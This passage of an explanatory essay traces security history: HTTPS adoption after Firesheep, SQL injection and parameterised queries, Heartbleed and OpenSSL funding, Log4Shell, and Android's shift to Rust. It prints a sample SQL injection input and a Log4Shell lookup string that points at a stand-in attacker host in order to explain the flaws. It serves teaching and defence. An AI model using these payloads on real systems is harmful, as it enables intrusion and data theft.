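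The case that Firesheep prompted a change is stronger for Facebook and Twitter. Facebook offered HTTPS as an option three months after Firesheep, and Rice (2011), in *Building More Secure Applications for Users*, gave public Wi-Fi as the reason. However, Facebook had told reporters in the week of Firesheep's release that it was already testing encrypted access. It had also just dealt with a much more serious attack in Tunisia, where the country's internet providers were recording Facebook users' passwords during the uprising (al-bab's *Tunisia and Facebook*, 2011). Facebook reportedly used HTTPS there first (Prince's *Facebook Pushes Social Authentication, HTTPS to Bolster Security*, 2011).

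Twitter followed with its own HTTPS option in March. Twitter (2011) also cited open Wi-Fi, and Dark Reading's *New 'Always use HTTPS' setting the next step toward default HTTPS* (2011) mentions Facebook's move and growing criticism of Twitter. Some of that criticism came from Senator Charles Schumer. A few weeks earlier, he had called on large sites, including Twitter, Yahoo and Amazon, to adopt HTTPS because of tools like Firesheep. Firesheep probably led sites to introduce these options some months sooner.

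Optional HTTPS protects only the users who turn it on. According to eWeek, the privacy researcher Christopher Soghoian complained that companies know users rarely change settings they don't understand. About 35% of Facebook users had HTTPS before the company began switching people over. That is a high share for an advanced setting, but it left most accounts exposed for two more years.

Facebook's *Secure browsing by default* (2013) explains the delay. Starting an encrypted connection took up to two extra round trips between the browser and the server, which added about 40 milliseconds for a user in Vancouver but could add 600 for one in Jakarta. Facebook dealt with this by placing servers around the world and letting returning browsers skip part of the exchange. It also had to get outside developers to encrypt the games and other applications that ran inside Facebook's pages, because browsers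 block unencrypted content within an encrypted page, and it gave them 150 days to do so. Some older phones could not use HTTPS properly at all.

### How the rest of the web followed

Google's *HTTPS encryption on the web* gives the share of pages that Chrome loads over HTTPS, using data from people who let the browser send statistics. Mozilla has a longer series for Firefox.

| Date | Measurement | HTTPS share |
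|---|---|---|
| 2014 | Pages loaded in Firefox | Under 30% |
| 2015 | Pages loaded in Chrome, by platform | About 30–45% |
| February 2017 | Pages loaded in Chrome on Windows, 13 large countries | 29% (South Korea) to 63% (United States) |
| About 2020 | Pages loaded in Chrome, by platform | About 95–99% |
| End of 2024 | Pages loaded in Firefox | Over 80% |
| 2025 | Pages loaded in Chrome, public sites only | About 97% (Linux) to over 99% (Android, Mac) |

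The 2017 figures come from *Measuring HTTPS Adoption on the Web* (Felt, Barnes and colleagues). The two browsers' figures are not directly comparable, because Mozilla's old series undercounts HTTPS. *The State of https Adoption on the Web* (Kerschbaumer, Braun and colleagues, 2025) used a newer method for one month in early 2025. About 92% of pages loaded over HTTPS, 5.5% came from local addresses such as home routers, and 2.4% loaded over plain HTTP. HTTPS use also varies widely by country, from 98% in Denmark to 51% in Sudan.

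Most of the rise came between 2015 and 2020, five to ten years after Firesheep, so other causes fit the dates better. Firesheep was also never a threat to sites without accounts.

Edward Snowden's disclosures about mass surveillance by the US National Security Agency began in June 2013. In March 2014 Google made HTTPS compulsory in Gmail. *Staying at forefront of email security* (Lidzborski, 2014) said this meant nobody could listen in between users and Google's servers. Google said the revelations were why it was urgently encrypting mail between its own data centres. Felt and colleagues also describe the industry's campaign for HTTPS as a response to public reports of surveillance and tampering. This is evidence that attacks mattered, though the attackers were governments. But many small sites needed an easier way to adopt HTTPS more than they needed persuading.

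To offer HTTPS, a site needs a certificate, a file in which a trusted organisation vouches that the server belongs to the named site. Certificates used to cost money, and installing and renewing them was fiddly. Aertsen (2016), in *How to bring HTTPS to the masses*, blames technical complexity and poor economic incentives for the slow spread of encryption. Let's Encrypt, a non-profit certificate authority that opened to the public in December 2015, made certificates free and automated the work. By January 2017 it had over 20 million active certificates. Its founders set up the organisation in May 2013, a month before the first Snowden story, so the disclosures cannot have prompted it, though they may have helped it find sponsors.

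Between April 2016 and February 2017, the share of about a million fairly active websites that supported HTTPS rose from 30% to 40%. Felt and colleagues credit Let's Encrypt and publishing platforms such as Squarespace, which host many small sites and could add HTTPS for all of them. Among 100 top sites, the share using HTTPS by default rose from 24% to 44% in a year. They attribute this rise to public demand and to new browser features that worked only over HTTPS. These explanations are informed guesses by people whose employers were promoting HTTPS. Kerschbaumer and colleagues list similar causes, add that search engines ranked encrypted sites higher, and do not try to separate their effects.

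Speed became less of an obstacle to HTTPS over time. Adam Langley, a Google engineer, reported in 2010 that Gmail's switch to HTTPS had needed no extra machines and that encryption took less than 1% of the processor load on its front-end servers. Processors were already fast enough for Google, and the remaining delay came mostly from distance, as Facebook found. In 2017 the security researcher Troy Hunt argued that HTTPS sites were no longer slow and that free services had made the switch easy (Slashdot's *HTTPS Adoption Has Reached the Tipping Point*).

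Browsers began warning about HTTP late in the web's move to HTTPS. Chrome and Firefox began warning about passwords and card numbers on HTTP pages in early 2017, and Chrome labelled every HTTP page "Not Secure" from 2018, when HTTPS already carried most browsing. A warning on most pages would have taught people to ignore warnings, so browser makers had to wait for wider adoption before pressing the remaining sites to switch. The last step came in October 2026, when Chrome began asking all users for permission before opening a public site without HTTPS. DeBlasio, Trouton and colleagues (2026), in *Chrome Now Warns Before Insecure HTTP Connections*, explain that the old label appeared only after the connection had exposed the user's data. In a trial of the new warning, half of users saw fewer than one a week, according to Thompson, Acer and colleagues (2025), in *HTTPS by default*. They had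 also contacted the companies behind the most HTTP traffic and found that many could switch without great difficulty but had never given it any attention.

### SQL injection and its fix

SQL is the language that most programs use to query databases. A shop's website might look up a customer's orders with a line like this:

```python
query = "SELECT * FROM orders WHERE email = '" + email + "'"
```

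The program glues whatever the visitor typed into the middle of a command. If the visitor types `' OR '1'='1` instead of an address, the database receives this:

```sql
SELECT * FROM orders WHERE email = '' OR '1'='1'
```

One equals one for every row in the table, so the database returns every customer's orders. Depending on the database, similar tricks can change or delete records, or give the attacker control of the server. A parameterised query removes the problem by sending the command and the visitor's text separately:

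```python
db.execute("SELECT * FROM orders WHERE email = ?", [email])
```

The database now searches for a customer whose address is exactly `' OR '1'='1` and finds nobody. The safe line takes no more code than the dangerous one. Its one real limitation is that a parameter can stand for a value but not for a table or column name. A programmer who lets visitors choose which column to sort by must handle that choice another way, such as by checking it against a fixed list.

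Hackers have publicly described SQL injection since December 1998, and developers knew how to fix it within weeks, according to Secure Code Warrior's *Happy birthday SQL injection, the bug that can't be squashed* (2020). Attacks have been frequent and expensive ever since. In 2020, one exposed 8.3 million accounts at Freepik, a stock image site.

The most damaging recent case began in May 2023, when the criminal group Cl0p used a SQL injection zero-day in MOVEit Transfer, a program that companies and public bodies use to send large files. Progress, its maker, patched three critical flaws between 31 May and 15 June, but Cl0p had already stolen data from many customers. Security Boulevard's *CISA, FBI Push Software Developers to Eliminate SQL Injection Flaws* (2024) cites the security firm Emsisoft's count of 2,769 affected organisations and almost 95 million people. Few of those people can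 have known that their data passed through MOVEit, let alone chosen it, so this is also a clear case of losses falling on outsiders.

In March 2024 the FBI and CISA, the US government's cybersecurity agency, responded to the MOVEit attacks with an alert urging software makers to eliminate SQL injection. CISA (2024) noted that manufacturers were still making products with the flaw after two decades of warnings. Weeks later CISA launched a pledge in which companies promise to reduce whole classes of flaw, with SQL injection given as an example. An editor of *Secure by Design Alert* (2024), a newsletter from the security training company SANS, called SQL injection the "least necessary" vulnerability and blamed the habit of releasing software quickly.

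Data on the frequency of SQL injection are mixed. MITRE, a non-profit that maintains the standard catalogue of software weaknesses, ranks them each year by how often they appear in published vulnerabilities and how severe those are. SQL injection came third in 2024 and second in 2025. OWASP, a volunteer group for web security, put injection flaws of all kinds first in 2017, third in 2021 and fifth in 2025. A rank can move because other flaws became more or less common, and MITRE's list counts a flaw in an obscure plug-in the same as one in a widely used product. The lists show that SQL injection is far from disappearing, but not whether a typical line of new database code is safer than it was in 2005.

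### Why HTTPS spread and safe queries did not

One reason the outcomes differed is that fewer people had to act to stop Firesheep than to stop SQL injection. Most page visits go to a small number of popular sites, and Thompson, Savage and colleagues (2018) found that these sites accounted for most of the encrypted traffic. When Facebook changed its default, over a billion people got HTTPS without doing anything, and its developers didn't have to remember it each time they wrote a new page. Squarespace could do the same for its customers, and a handful of browser makers could press other sites to switch.

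Nobody has such a switch for SQL injection. Every programmer must write every query safely for as long as the program exists. Suppose a careful team writes 999 of every 1,000 queries safely, and its product contains 2,000 queries. The expected number of flaws is two, though an attacker needs only one, and the chance that there are none is about 14%. In the adoption rule above, the cost C of a single safe query is close to zero, but the cost of never making a mistake is high, and attacks do not lower it.

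Outsiders can also see whether a site uses HTTPS. If it doesn't, browsers can automatically warn visitors, search engines can rank the site lower, and researchers can include it in published lists of insecure sites, all of which raise the site's share of the loss. Customers who buy a file-transfer program face the lemons problem, because they have no comparable way to know whether one of its queries is unsafe.

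Parameterised queries are in roughly the position HTTPS had at Facebook in 2011, available but used only by those who choose them. Firefox is a more recent example of how badly opt-in security works. Only about two million users ever turned on its strict HTTPS-Only mode, and a third of them turned it off again. Programmers know more about security than most browser users, but they are busy, and the unsafe query works in testing.

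### Safe-by-default frameworks at Google

Christoph Kern, a security engineer at Google, has spent years on the alternative of removing the unsafe choice. Kern told OpenSSF, an open-source security foundation, that injection flaws are so common because the underlying interfaces accept any string and leave the developer to make sure it is safe. *Safe Coding* (Kern, 2025) traces memory-safety flaws to the same root, since C also relies on the programmer to satisfy conditions that the language doesn't check. Kern concludes that training developers and hunting for bugs afterwards have not reduced either kind of flaw enough. Microsoft's experience with the Security Development Lifecycle suggests the same.

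To prevent SQL injection, Google uses a special type of text called TrustedSqlString. Its database library accepts only this type, which programmers can build only from text written in the program's own source code. Visitors' input arrives while the program is running, so it can't become part of a command and has to be passed as a parameter. The glued-together query from the shop example would not compile. Rare exceptions, such as a tool that lets staff type their own queries, go through an explicitly marked route that security engineers can review. Rust's "unsafe" keyword likewise marks exceptions so that they can be reviewed.

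The results appear to be good. In Google's book on secure and reliable systems, the engineers report that SQL injection stops being an issue where teams use the library. A related flaw is cross-site scripting, in which an attacker gets a website to run the attacker's code in other visitors' browsers. Google reported in 2024 that hundreds of complex web applications built on its safe frameworks had together averaged fewer than one report of this flaw a year. This is Google's own account, without a published comparison with similar applications that did not use the frameworks. Still, better training or luck would hardly explain a rate that close to zero, and anybody can check the mechanism by trying to compile an unsafe query.

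Attacks seem to have played a modest part in Google's decision. According to *Software Security @Scale* (Kern, 2024), Google has tens of thousands of developers, billions of lines of code and roughly one security engineer for every few hundred developers. Those engineers could never review every query, so Google changed one library instead, which took less work. Google could also make its teams use that library, a power that most organisations lack. A company like Progress can adopt such a rule for its own code, but the makers of the popular programming languages and database libraries would have to break millions of existing programs to impose it on everyone. Many web frameworks now generate parameterised queries automatically, which helps, but they usually also let a hurried programmer write the query by hand.

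## Heartbleed and the upkeep of OpenSSL

Much of the web's move to HTTPS depended on OpenSSL, a free library that the Slapper worm had targeted in 2002. OpenSSL handled encryption for Apache and Nginx, which together ran about two-thirds of the million most popular websites. In April 2014, a flaw in the library called Heartbleed became the most famous software bug in years.

### A missing length check

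OpenSSL's heartbeat feature, released in March 2012, let a computer check that the other end of an encrypted connection was still there by sending a short message for it to echo. The message included its own length, which OpenSSL used without checking it against what had arrived. An attacker could send the five letters `hello`, give the length as 60,000, and receive `hello` followed by 59,995 bytes of whatever lay next to it in the server's memory. Those bytes could include passwords or the private key that proves the server's identity.

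The fix was a length check, which Ericson (2026) reproduces in *How the OpenSSL community was built on Heartbleed*:

```c
if (1 + 2 + payload + 16 > s->s3->rrec.length)
    return 0;
```

A heartbeat has one byte for its type, two for the stated length, the text and at least 16 bytes of padding. In the attack above, the stated length brings the total to 60,019 bytes, but only 24 arrived, so a patched server drops the message. A program written in Rust or Java would not have read past the end of the message, even without the check.

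Neel Mehta of Google found the flaw on 21 March 2014, two years after OpenSSL released the faulty code, and the Finnish security company Codenomicon found it independently 12 days later. Codenomicon gave it a name, a logo and a website, and bought the web address two days before OpenSSL announced the flaw on 7 April.

### How websites responded

Nobody had counted the vulnerable sites before the announcement, but *The Matter of Heartbleed* (2014), by Durumeric, Kasten and colleagues, estimates that 24% to 55% of the HTTPS sites among the million most popular were initially vulnerable. Two days after the announcement, 60% of these HTTPS sites still supported heartbeats, and 91% of those ran server software known to be affected, which gives the upper limit of about 55%. The lower limit is based on support for two newer versions of the encryption protocol, which OpenSSL had introduced in the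 same release as heartbeats. Before the announcement, about 33% of sites supported these versions, and 73% of those ran affected servers.

Large sites patched quickly. At least 44 of the top 100 had been vulnerable, and only five still were after 22 hours. Across the million sites, the vulnerable share of those with HTTPS fell from 11.5% two days after the announcement to 3.1% in early June, and most of that fall came in the first two weeks. Durumeric and colleagues also emailed the operators of servers that were still vulnerable, in two waves so that they could compare the groups. Operators who got the warning patched 47% more often, so part of the delay came from operators who did not know their servers were vulnerable.

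If an attacker had already copied a site's private key, the site needed a new key and a new certificate as well as the patch. Of the sites still vulnerable after two days, 73% patched within a month, but only 10% replaced their certificates. Of those replacing them, 14% kept the old key, which made the new certificate useless. *Analysis of SSL Certificate Reissues and Revocations in the Wake of Heartbleed* (2014) found that site owners had not reissued over 73% of vulnerable certificates three weeks after the announcement.

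The known thefts were mostly small. Durumeric and colleagues saw no attacks in traffic recorded at four sites before the announcement, but attempts from almost 700 sources afterwards. Thieves took about $6,500 in bitcoin from customers of one exchange, which repaid them, and about 900 taxpayers' social insurance numbers from the Canada Revenue Agency. Attackers also reportedly used Heartbleed to break into a US hospital chain that lost records of 4.5 million patients, but that came to light only in August, after the main response had begun. Exposure and publicity therefore prompted the response to Heartbleed more than losses did.

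### One full-time developer

Steve Marquess, who handled OpenSSL's money, described its finances in an essay that Zeus News reprinted. The project's foundation received about $2,000 a year in donations, and its total annual income had never reached $1 million. It earned most of its income by hiring out its developers at $250 an hour, nearly always to add a feature or obtain a certificate that one customer wanted. Marquess thought the certification work, which the US Defense Department had funded for over a decade, did nothing for the overall quality of the code. Only one developer, Stephen Henson, had no other job, and nobody had time to start on about $100,000 of signed contracts.

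In the week after the announcement, about 200 people donated roughly $9,000, enough for 36 hours of work at the foundation's rate. Marquess thought that the project needed at least six full-time developers and that companies selling products built on OpenSSL should pay for them.

On 24 April, 17 days after the Heartbleed announcement, the Linux Foundation, a consortium that supports open-source software, launched the Core Infrastructure Initiative to fund neglected projects. By the end of May it had raised $5.4 million and had 17 corporate backers, including Google, Microsoft, Amazon and Facebook, according to eWEEK's *Linux Foundation's CII Funds Efforts to Prevent the Next Heartbleed*. A year later the total was still only about $5.5 million, spread over three years (eWEEK, 2015). If the 17 companies had shared that equally, each would have paid about $108,000 a year, less than the cost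 of one engineer.

The Linux Foundation (2014) named three projects for the first grants: OpenSSL, the remote-login program OpenSSH, and the protocol that synchronizes computers' clocks. OpenSSL got two full-time developers and a security audit. The initiative later gave $60,000 to Werner Koch, who was going broke while maintaining the email encryption program GNU Privacy Guard. The Linux Foundation's *Answering the Call for Werner Kochs Everywhere* says there were hundreds of similar stories.

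### Forks and rewrites

Other programmers thought OpenSSL could not be fixed, or at least that a shared version was not worth keeping. Some made forks, which are separate versions that start from a copy of the code, and others wrote replacements.

| Response | Date | Who did or paid for it | What changed | Depth |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Length check | April 2014 | OpenSSL's volunteers | One flaw fixed | Repair |
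| Core Infrastructure Initiative grant | 2014–2017 | 17 companies | Two developers and an audit | Mostly repair |
| LibreSSL (fork) | April 2014 | OpenBSD's volunteers | Old code deleted, safer memory handling | Hardening |
| BoringSSL (fork) | June 2014 | Google | Smaller library for Google's own products | Hardening |
| s2n (new library in C) | June 2015 | Amazon | About 6,000 lines, with later proofs of some parts | Hardening, some prevention |
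| Rustls (new library in Rust) | 2016 onwards | One programmer, later several funders | Protocol code in a memory-safe language | Prevention |

LibreSSL's developers objected that OpenSSL managed its own pool of memory instead of requesting it from the operating system each time, which bypassed protections that might have made a Heartbleed attack crash the server. They removed that layer, along with tens of thousands of lines of code supporting obsolete computers.

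BoringSSL, Google's fork of OpenSSL, had less to do with Heartbleed than its timing suggests. Adam Langley, the engineer who announced it, explained that Google had maintained more than 70 of its own changes to OpenSSL for years and that reapplying them to each new version had become too much work. Because Google controls Chrome and Android, it could then move billions of users to BoringSSL without asking them to do anything.

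Rustls went furthest, but it began too late for Heartbleed to be its direct cause. Joseph Birr-Pixton started it in 2016, a year after Rust's first stable release. Memory-safe encryption libraries already existed in Java and Go, but those languages need a garbage collector, which makes their libraries awkward to use inside a web server written in C. Rustls received substantial funding only in 2021, through the non-profit that runs Let's Encrypt. Google, Amazon, the hosting company Fly.io and a German government fund have paid for work on it.

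Rustls is now a standard choice for programs written in Rust, and since 2024 a compatibility layer has let Nginx use it in place of OpenSSL. But Apache and Nginx still use OpenSSL by default, so server operators must choose to switch. Rustls also relies by default on a library in C and assembly language for the mathematics of encryption. It therefore protects the code that reads messages from strangers, where Heartbleed was, but not the encryption code.

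### OpenSSL in 2026

OpenSSL eventually got the staff Marquess had asked for, and kept them with income from support contracts rather than the initiative's grant. OpenSSL (2023) describes the grant as a short-term measure and its corporate sponsorship as too small and unstable to hire people. Support contracts have been its main source of income since 2020. By 2023 about 70 customers were paying for technical help, for fixes to old versions they had not yet replaced, or for the right to put their own brand on OpenSSL's government security certificate. That paid for eight full-time staff. According to the OpenSSL Corporation (2026), the commercial arm had 21 staff by the end of 2025 and was funded entirely by such contracts. The corporation's figures show that 86% of customers renewed.

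Heartbleed gave OpenSSL time and attention, and Ericson, who works for the OpenSSL Foundation, calls it good for the community. The lasting money came from customers who needed certificates or wanted to put off an upgrade. In the adoption rule, that money is part of b, the benefit unrelated to attacks.

More staff did not stop memory-safety flaws. On 27 January 2026 OpenSSL fixed 12 vulnerabilities, including stack and heap overflows, and the worst could let an attacker run code remotely (Paganini, 2026, *OpenSSL issued security updates to fix 12 flaws, including Remote Code Execution*). An AI system from the security firm AISLE found all 12, according to the firm's account, which Schneier (2026) quotes in *AI Found Twelve New Vulnerabilities in OpenSSL*. OpenSSL's *Vulnerabilities 3.6* also credits a researcher from another firm with one of them. AISLE calls the flaws zero-days, meaning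 only that OpenSSL's developers had not known of them.

In September, OpenSSL fixed a flaw that resembled Heartbleed more closely, a bug in its code for a related protocol, DTLS, that could leak a program's memory. The Hacker News' *OpenSSL Fixes High-Severity DTLS Flaw That Can Leak Heap Memory Unencrypted* (2026) reported no attacks using it. A release on 1 December fixed 16 more vulnerabilities. Five were in OpenSSL's code for QUIC, a newer protocol for encrypted connections, and involved errors such as using memory after its release and reading memory before anything had been stored in it (Linuxiac's *OpenSSL 4.1.1 Released with Fixes for 16 Security Vulnerabilities*, 2026). OpenSSL first shipped its QUIC code in 2023, nine years after Heartbleed, when it already had paid staff, but the developers still wrote it in C.

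OpenSSL's developers now also run AISLE's tool on proposed changes to the code. AISLE reports that in 2025 this caught several flaws before release, including two errors in releasing memory. This is better than patching flaws after release, but the same kinds of flaw remain possible. People also have to act on the findings. Caswell, an executive director at OpenSSL, writes in *AI is Finding More Vulnerabilities But Open Source Needs More People* (2026) that about 400 reports over 12 months yielded 43 confirmed vulnerabilities, and that each false report took about as much expert attention as a real one. Caswell fears that some of the lessons of Heartbleed are fading.

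### Why nobody paid beforehand

Before 2014, OpenSSL's developers did the work of preventing flaws, but the losses from any flaws fell on its users. The developers' share of the loss, s, was close to zero, so pride in their work was almost their only reason to be careful.

The companies that used OpenSSL stood to lose from its poor upkeep, but each had little reason to pay for better upkeep alone. Suppose that proper upkeep costs $2 million a year and saves each of 1,000 companies $20,000. Together they save $20 million, ten times the cost, but a company paying alone would spend $100 for each dollar it saved. Each does better by waiting for someone else to pay, so nobody maintains the library properly. A company with 200 times the usual stake would save $4 million and could sensibly pay the full $2 million itself. Google and Amazon were in roughly that position, and both chose to build libraries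 they controlled.

A famous flaw changes this for a while. Companies notice their dependence at the same time, and a neutral organisation can collect money from them while their customers are asking questions. A 2014 article in ACM Queue called this "a game you can win only by losing first" and warned that many other projects were in the same state. Publicity led the initiative to fund OpenSSL and a few other well-known projects, but it had no comparable way to find the next neglected library.

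### Log4Shell

The next such flaw was in Log4j, a free Java library that programs use to log events. If a log message contained text like `${jndi:ldap://attacker.example/x}`, Log4j contacted that address and could download and run a program from it. An attacker only had to get the text into a log, for instance by typing it into a login form as a user name. The flaw, known as Log4Shell, became public in December 2021, and attackers were using it widely within days.

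Java is a memory-safe language, so rewriting Log4j in Rust would not have helped. The cause was a dangerous feature that few people needed and that was on by default. Within a week the maintainers had removed the feature from log messages, which was an easy form of prevention. Cleaning up the many products that contained old copies of Log4j took years.

Funding followed much the same course as after Heartbleed. A few volunteers with other jobs maintained Log4j, and the money raised in 2014 had not reached them, although large companies depended on their work. The White House quickly called a meeting in January 2022, and in May OpenSSF, which had absorbed the Core Infrastructure Initiative, proposed a plan costing about $150 million over two years. Companies initially pledged $30 million, over five times what the initiative had raised but only a fifth of what the plan required. The German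 fund that supported Rustls later paid Log4j's developers too.

In October 2026 two critical flaws in PHP, the programming language behind about 70% of websites, led companies and governments to take hundreds of sites offline. The foundation that pays PHP's developers was set up in 2021 because a leading developer had moved on, not in response to an attack. At the end of 2025 it had 536 sponsors and 11 contracted developers, some of them part-time (The PHP Foundation, 2026). Its director called it "under-funded" and said it had one full-time staff member (Reuters, 2026).

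The PHP flaws had survived partly for lack of people. Greig (2026) reports in *PHP says AI review of critical bugs first sparked alarm in August* that an audit had pointed to one of them in 2024, but the few developers who understood that part of PHP were busy and could not agree on a fix that would not break existing sites. In *The Vulnerability Apocalypse and Why We Should Fund Open Source*, Quintin (2026) called on companies to contribute money and people, much as Marquess had 12 years earlier. The Core Infrastructure Initiative had formed 17 days after Heartbleed. A month after the PHP flaws, Nils Adermann, a board member of the PHP Foundation, was "a bit pessimistic" that people would care enough to act, according to Slashdot's *Will AI-Fueled Cyberattacks Lead to Better Funding for Critical Open Source Projects?* (2026).

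## Android's move to Rust

Android's code had the same kinds of memory-safety flaw as OpenSSL's. Google's Android team began writing new code in Rust, while OpenSSL's developers were still writing C years after Heartbleed. Memory-safety flaws fell from 76% of Android's vulnerabilities in 2019 to less than 20% in 2025, although most of the old C and C++ code is still in place.

Android's designers chose Java, a memory-safe language, for apps on the first Android phone in 2008, and ran each app in a sandbox, which limits what a program can reach. Kralevich (2017), in *Honey, I Shrunk the Attack Surface*, says they did this to avoid repeating the security mistakes of older consumer systems. But the code that played video, ran Bluetooth and controlled the hardware was in C and C++, and much of it handled data from strangers.

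### Stagefright and monthly updates

In April 2015 the security researcher Joshua Drake sent Google patches for flaws in libstagefright, the library Android used to process audio and video. Several were integer overflows, which happen when a number grows too large for the space a program gives it. A 32-bit number cannot exceed 4,294,967,295, and adding 1 to that gives 0. If a video file declares a caption of 4,294,967,295 bytes and the program tries to reserve one byte more than that, it reserves none, then copies the caption over whatever lies next in memory.

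Google (2015) rated the worst of the flaws critical because an attacker could run code on a phone through a media file on a web page, in an email or in a picture message. Google's messaging apps had been automatically passing incoming media to the vulnerable service, so the phone's owner might not have to open anything. Neowin reported that an estimated 95% of active devices were still unprotected when the flaws became public that summer. On 5 August Google began sending monthly security updates to its Nexus phones, starting with fixes for Stagefright (Pixel Envy, *Android Security Fixes to Be Pushed to Nexus Devices Monthly*). Other manufacturers had to prepare updates for their own phones.

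Eighteen months later, Adrian Ludwig, Google's director of Android security, said the company had no confirmed evidence that anyone had used the flaws against users, according to eWeek's *How Google Secures Over a Billion Android Users* (2017). Google had an interest in saying so, and Android Authority's *Android security scares are all hype, no substance, suggests Google engineer* (2017) points out that the company's data came from a scanning service that does not cover phones without Google's app store, such as those sold in China. Still, widespread attacks would probably have left some trace. The monthly updates, like the response to Heartbleed, followed a researcher's warning rather than a known loss.

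### Four years of hardening

Google's larger response to Stagefright was to make such flaws harder to exploit. Austin (2017), a member of the Android security team, presented the choice on two slides of the talk *Your Move*: "We could try to eliminate all bugs" and "Or, we can make exploitation harder..."

Until 2016 a single program, mediaserver, handled nearly all of Android's audio and video, and it had gained more privileges with each new feature. Android 7 split it into several programs with few privileges each. The one that reads media files could make only 42 of the 364 kinds of request that the kernel accepts on 32-bit Arm phones, so an attacker who took it over needed another flaw to get further. Google also compiled the media code with checks that stop a program when an integer overflows. Google (2021) says in a January post on hardening that the critical flaws reported from Stagefright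 onwards led to the split.

Some of the hardening predated Stagefright. Android's main system for restricting programs, SELinux, dates from 2011 by Google's account, and Android 5.0 fully enforced it from October 2014. There is good evidence that it hampered real attackers. In CIA documents that WikiLeaks published in 2017, the agency's developers complained that SELinux had become too restrictive for one of their phone implants to work. The media changes seem to have helped too, since Google received no reports of critical, internet-reachable flaws in the media software in 2020. According to the same post, though, researchers flock to components where others have already found flaws, so reports may have fallen partly because they had moved on.

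In *Queue the Hardening Enhancements*, Vander Stoep and Zhang (2019) reported that use-after-free errors, integer overflows, and reads or writes outside a buffer made up 90% of the previous year's high-severity vulnerabilities. A different language would have prevented most of these, but as late as May 2019 their plan for Android's existing components was to contain risky code with more sandboxes and to add more checks to defend against the flaws they assumed it had.

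Those defences used processing time and memory. The integer checks slowed some functions so much that engineers reviewed those functions by hand and turned the checks off for them. Each new sandbox needed its own process, which used memory and delayed messages between programs. Cheap phones were least able to handle this extra load.

### Safer languages for new code

The Android team began moving new development to memory-safe languages around 2019. Google (2024) attributes this to "the increasing cost and complexity of managing memory safety vulnerabilities". Java and Kotlin could take over some of the work but not the lowest layers, where programs need direct control of memory. Rust could be used there, and in April 2021 Google (2021) announced that Android would support it for the operating system itself. Engineers had spent 18 months, from around October 2019, preparing the compilers,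 tests and training.

The table sets out the reasons that Google gave at each step.

| Date | Change | Google's stated reason | Depth |
|---|---|---|---|
| August 2015 | Monthly updates for Nexus phones | Faster delivery of fixes, starting with Stagefright | Repair |
| 2016 | Media software split into restricted programs | Many critical flaws since Stagefright, often reachable remotely | Hardening |
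| 2019 | Memory-safe languages for new code | Rising cost and complexity of managing memory-safety flaws | Prevention |
| April 2021 | Rust for the operating system | Crashes, about 70% of high-severity vulnerabilities, limits of sandboxing and bug-finding | Prevention |
| November 2025 | Rust for the link between Android's Quick Share and Apple's AirDrop | The code reads data that another device sends over the air | Prevention |

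The 2021 announcement called memory-safe languages "the most cost-effective means for preventing memory bugs". One reason it gave was that Google's tools now found bugs faster than people could fix them. In a complicated C++ component, only a handful of engineers might be able to write or review a fix, and some fixes were wrong. The other reason was that Android required C or C++ code reading untrusted data to run in a tightly restricted sandbox, while Rust code could safely run inside an existing process.

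Android's code for ultra-wideband, a short-range radio that locates nearby devices, is written in Rust, so it runs without a separate process. Google (2022) reports that this saved several megabytes of memory on each phone.

### The part that attacks played

Attacks explain Android's hardening better than its move to Rust. Stagefright came just before the monthly updates and the media split, and Google named it as the cause. Nothing similar happened in 2019. The team's stated reasons then were mostly about money, engineers' time and reliability, and Google's *Memory safety* lists crashes before security. Android phones were reporting millions of crashes in C and C++ code every day, and Google traced most of those it investigated to memory-safety bugs, which crash phones even when no one is attacking them.

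Attackers contributed indirectly. Memory-safety flaws accounted for 78% of the Android vulnerabilities that Google had confirmed in real attacks over the few years to 2022. The cost of fixing flaws, which Google complained about, also exists only because people look for flaws and might exploit them. Otherwise, Google could have fixed the crashes that users noticed and left the rest. But a company can bear that cost for many years without changing languages. Microsoft had the same 70% share of memory-safety flaws, yet Windows moved to Rust much more slowly. Windows had also suffered Blaster, Conficker and WannaCry, while Android had no confirmed Stagefright victims. If attacks decided how far a company moved to safer languages, Microsoft should have gone further than Google.

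A better explanation is that prevention had become less burdensome relative to hardening. Rust had been stable since 2015 and needed no garbage collector, while each extra layer of hardening added a greater burden than the last. Google also avoided the largest task in changing languages by leaving nearly all the old code alone. It did so because it judged in 2021 that rewriting Android's tens of millions of lines was "simply not feasible" even if every engineer on the team worked on it, though AI-assisted rewriting may change that judgement.

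### Why changing only new code works

A product with tens of millions of lines of old C++ can become safer if its programmers write new code in a memory-safe language, because flaws are concentrated in new code. Google found in 2021 that about half of Android's memory-safety bugs were less than a year old. People find and fix flaws over time, so code that is otherwise left alone gets safer.

The 2024 post expresses this as a formula. If a flaw survives for λ years on average and the chance of somebody finding it is the same each year, then the density of flaws in code of age t is

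density(t) = density(0) × e^(−t/λ)

Google measured an average flaw lifetime of about 2.5 years in Android and Chromium, the code base behind the Chrome browser. Five-year-old code therefore has e², or 7.4, times fewer flaws per line than new code. A 2022 academic study of open-source projects found longer lifetimes, which give a ratio of 3.4.

Suppose that a team has written a million lines of C++ a year for ten years, and that each million starts with 1,000 memory-safety flaws. With an average lifetime of 2.5 years, the flaws left are:

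| Age of the code | Flaws left per million lines |
|---|---|
| New | 1,000 |
| 1 year | 670 |
| 2 years | 449 |
| 3 years | 301 |
| 4 years | 202 |
| 5 to 9 years | 135, 91, 61, 41 and 27 |

The ten million lines contain about 2,980 flaws, a third of them in the newest million lines. The oldest five million lines contain only 355, so rewriting them in Rust would remove at most that many. Writing the next million lines in Rust would avoid 1,000 flaws, which is 14 times as many per line of Rust. After five years of writing only Rust, about 400 flaws would remain, compared with about 3,000 if the team had stayed with C++.

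Companies change languages gradually, so Google's simulation assumed that new development would take ten years to move to memory-safe languages and that the code base would double every six years. Memory-safety flaws fell sharply by the end of the simulation, even though the product contained more C and C++ than at the start.

The formula is only approximate. An average lifetime of 2.5 years implies that people find a third of flaws within a year, but Google's 2021 figure was half, so the newest code may be even worse than the formula assumes. The average also counts only flaws that have been found. Old code could hold many others that a better search method could expose all at once, so the strategy depends on continued repair of old code. Google has also made exceptions for especially exposed code, replacing Chromium's C++ readers for PNG images, web fonts and JSON data with Rust versions.

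### What the vulnerability counts measure

Google counts the flaws it rates critical or high in Android's monthly security bulletins. Outside researchers report some of these flaws through Google's reward programme, and Google's own staff report others.

| Year | Memory-safety flaws | Share of all flaws counted | Other flaws (calculated) |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2019 | 223 | 76% | 70 |
| 2022 | 85 | 36% | 151 |
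| 2024 | 36 (projected) | 24% | 114 |
| 2025 | No count given | Below 20% | Unknown |

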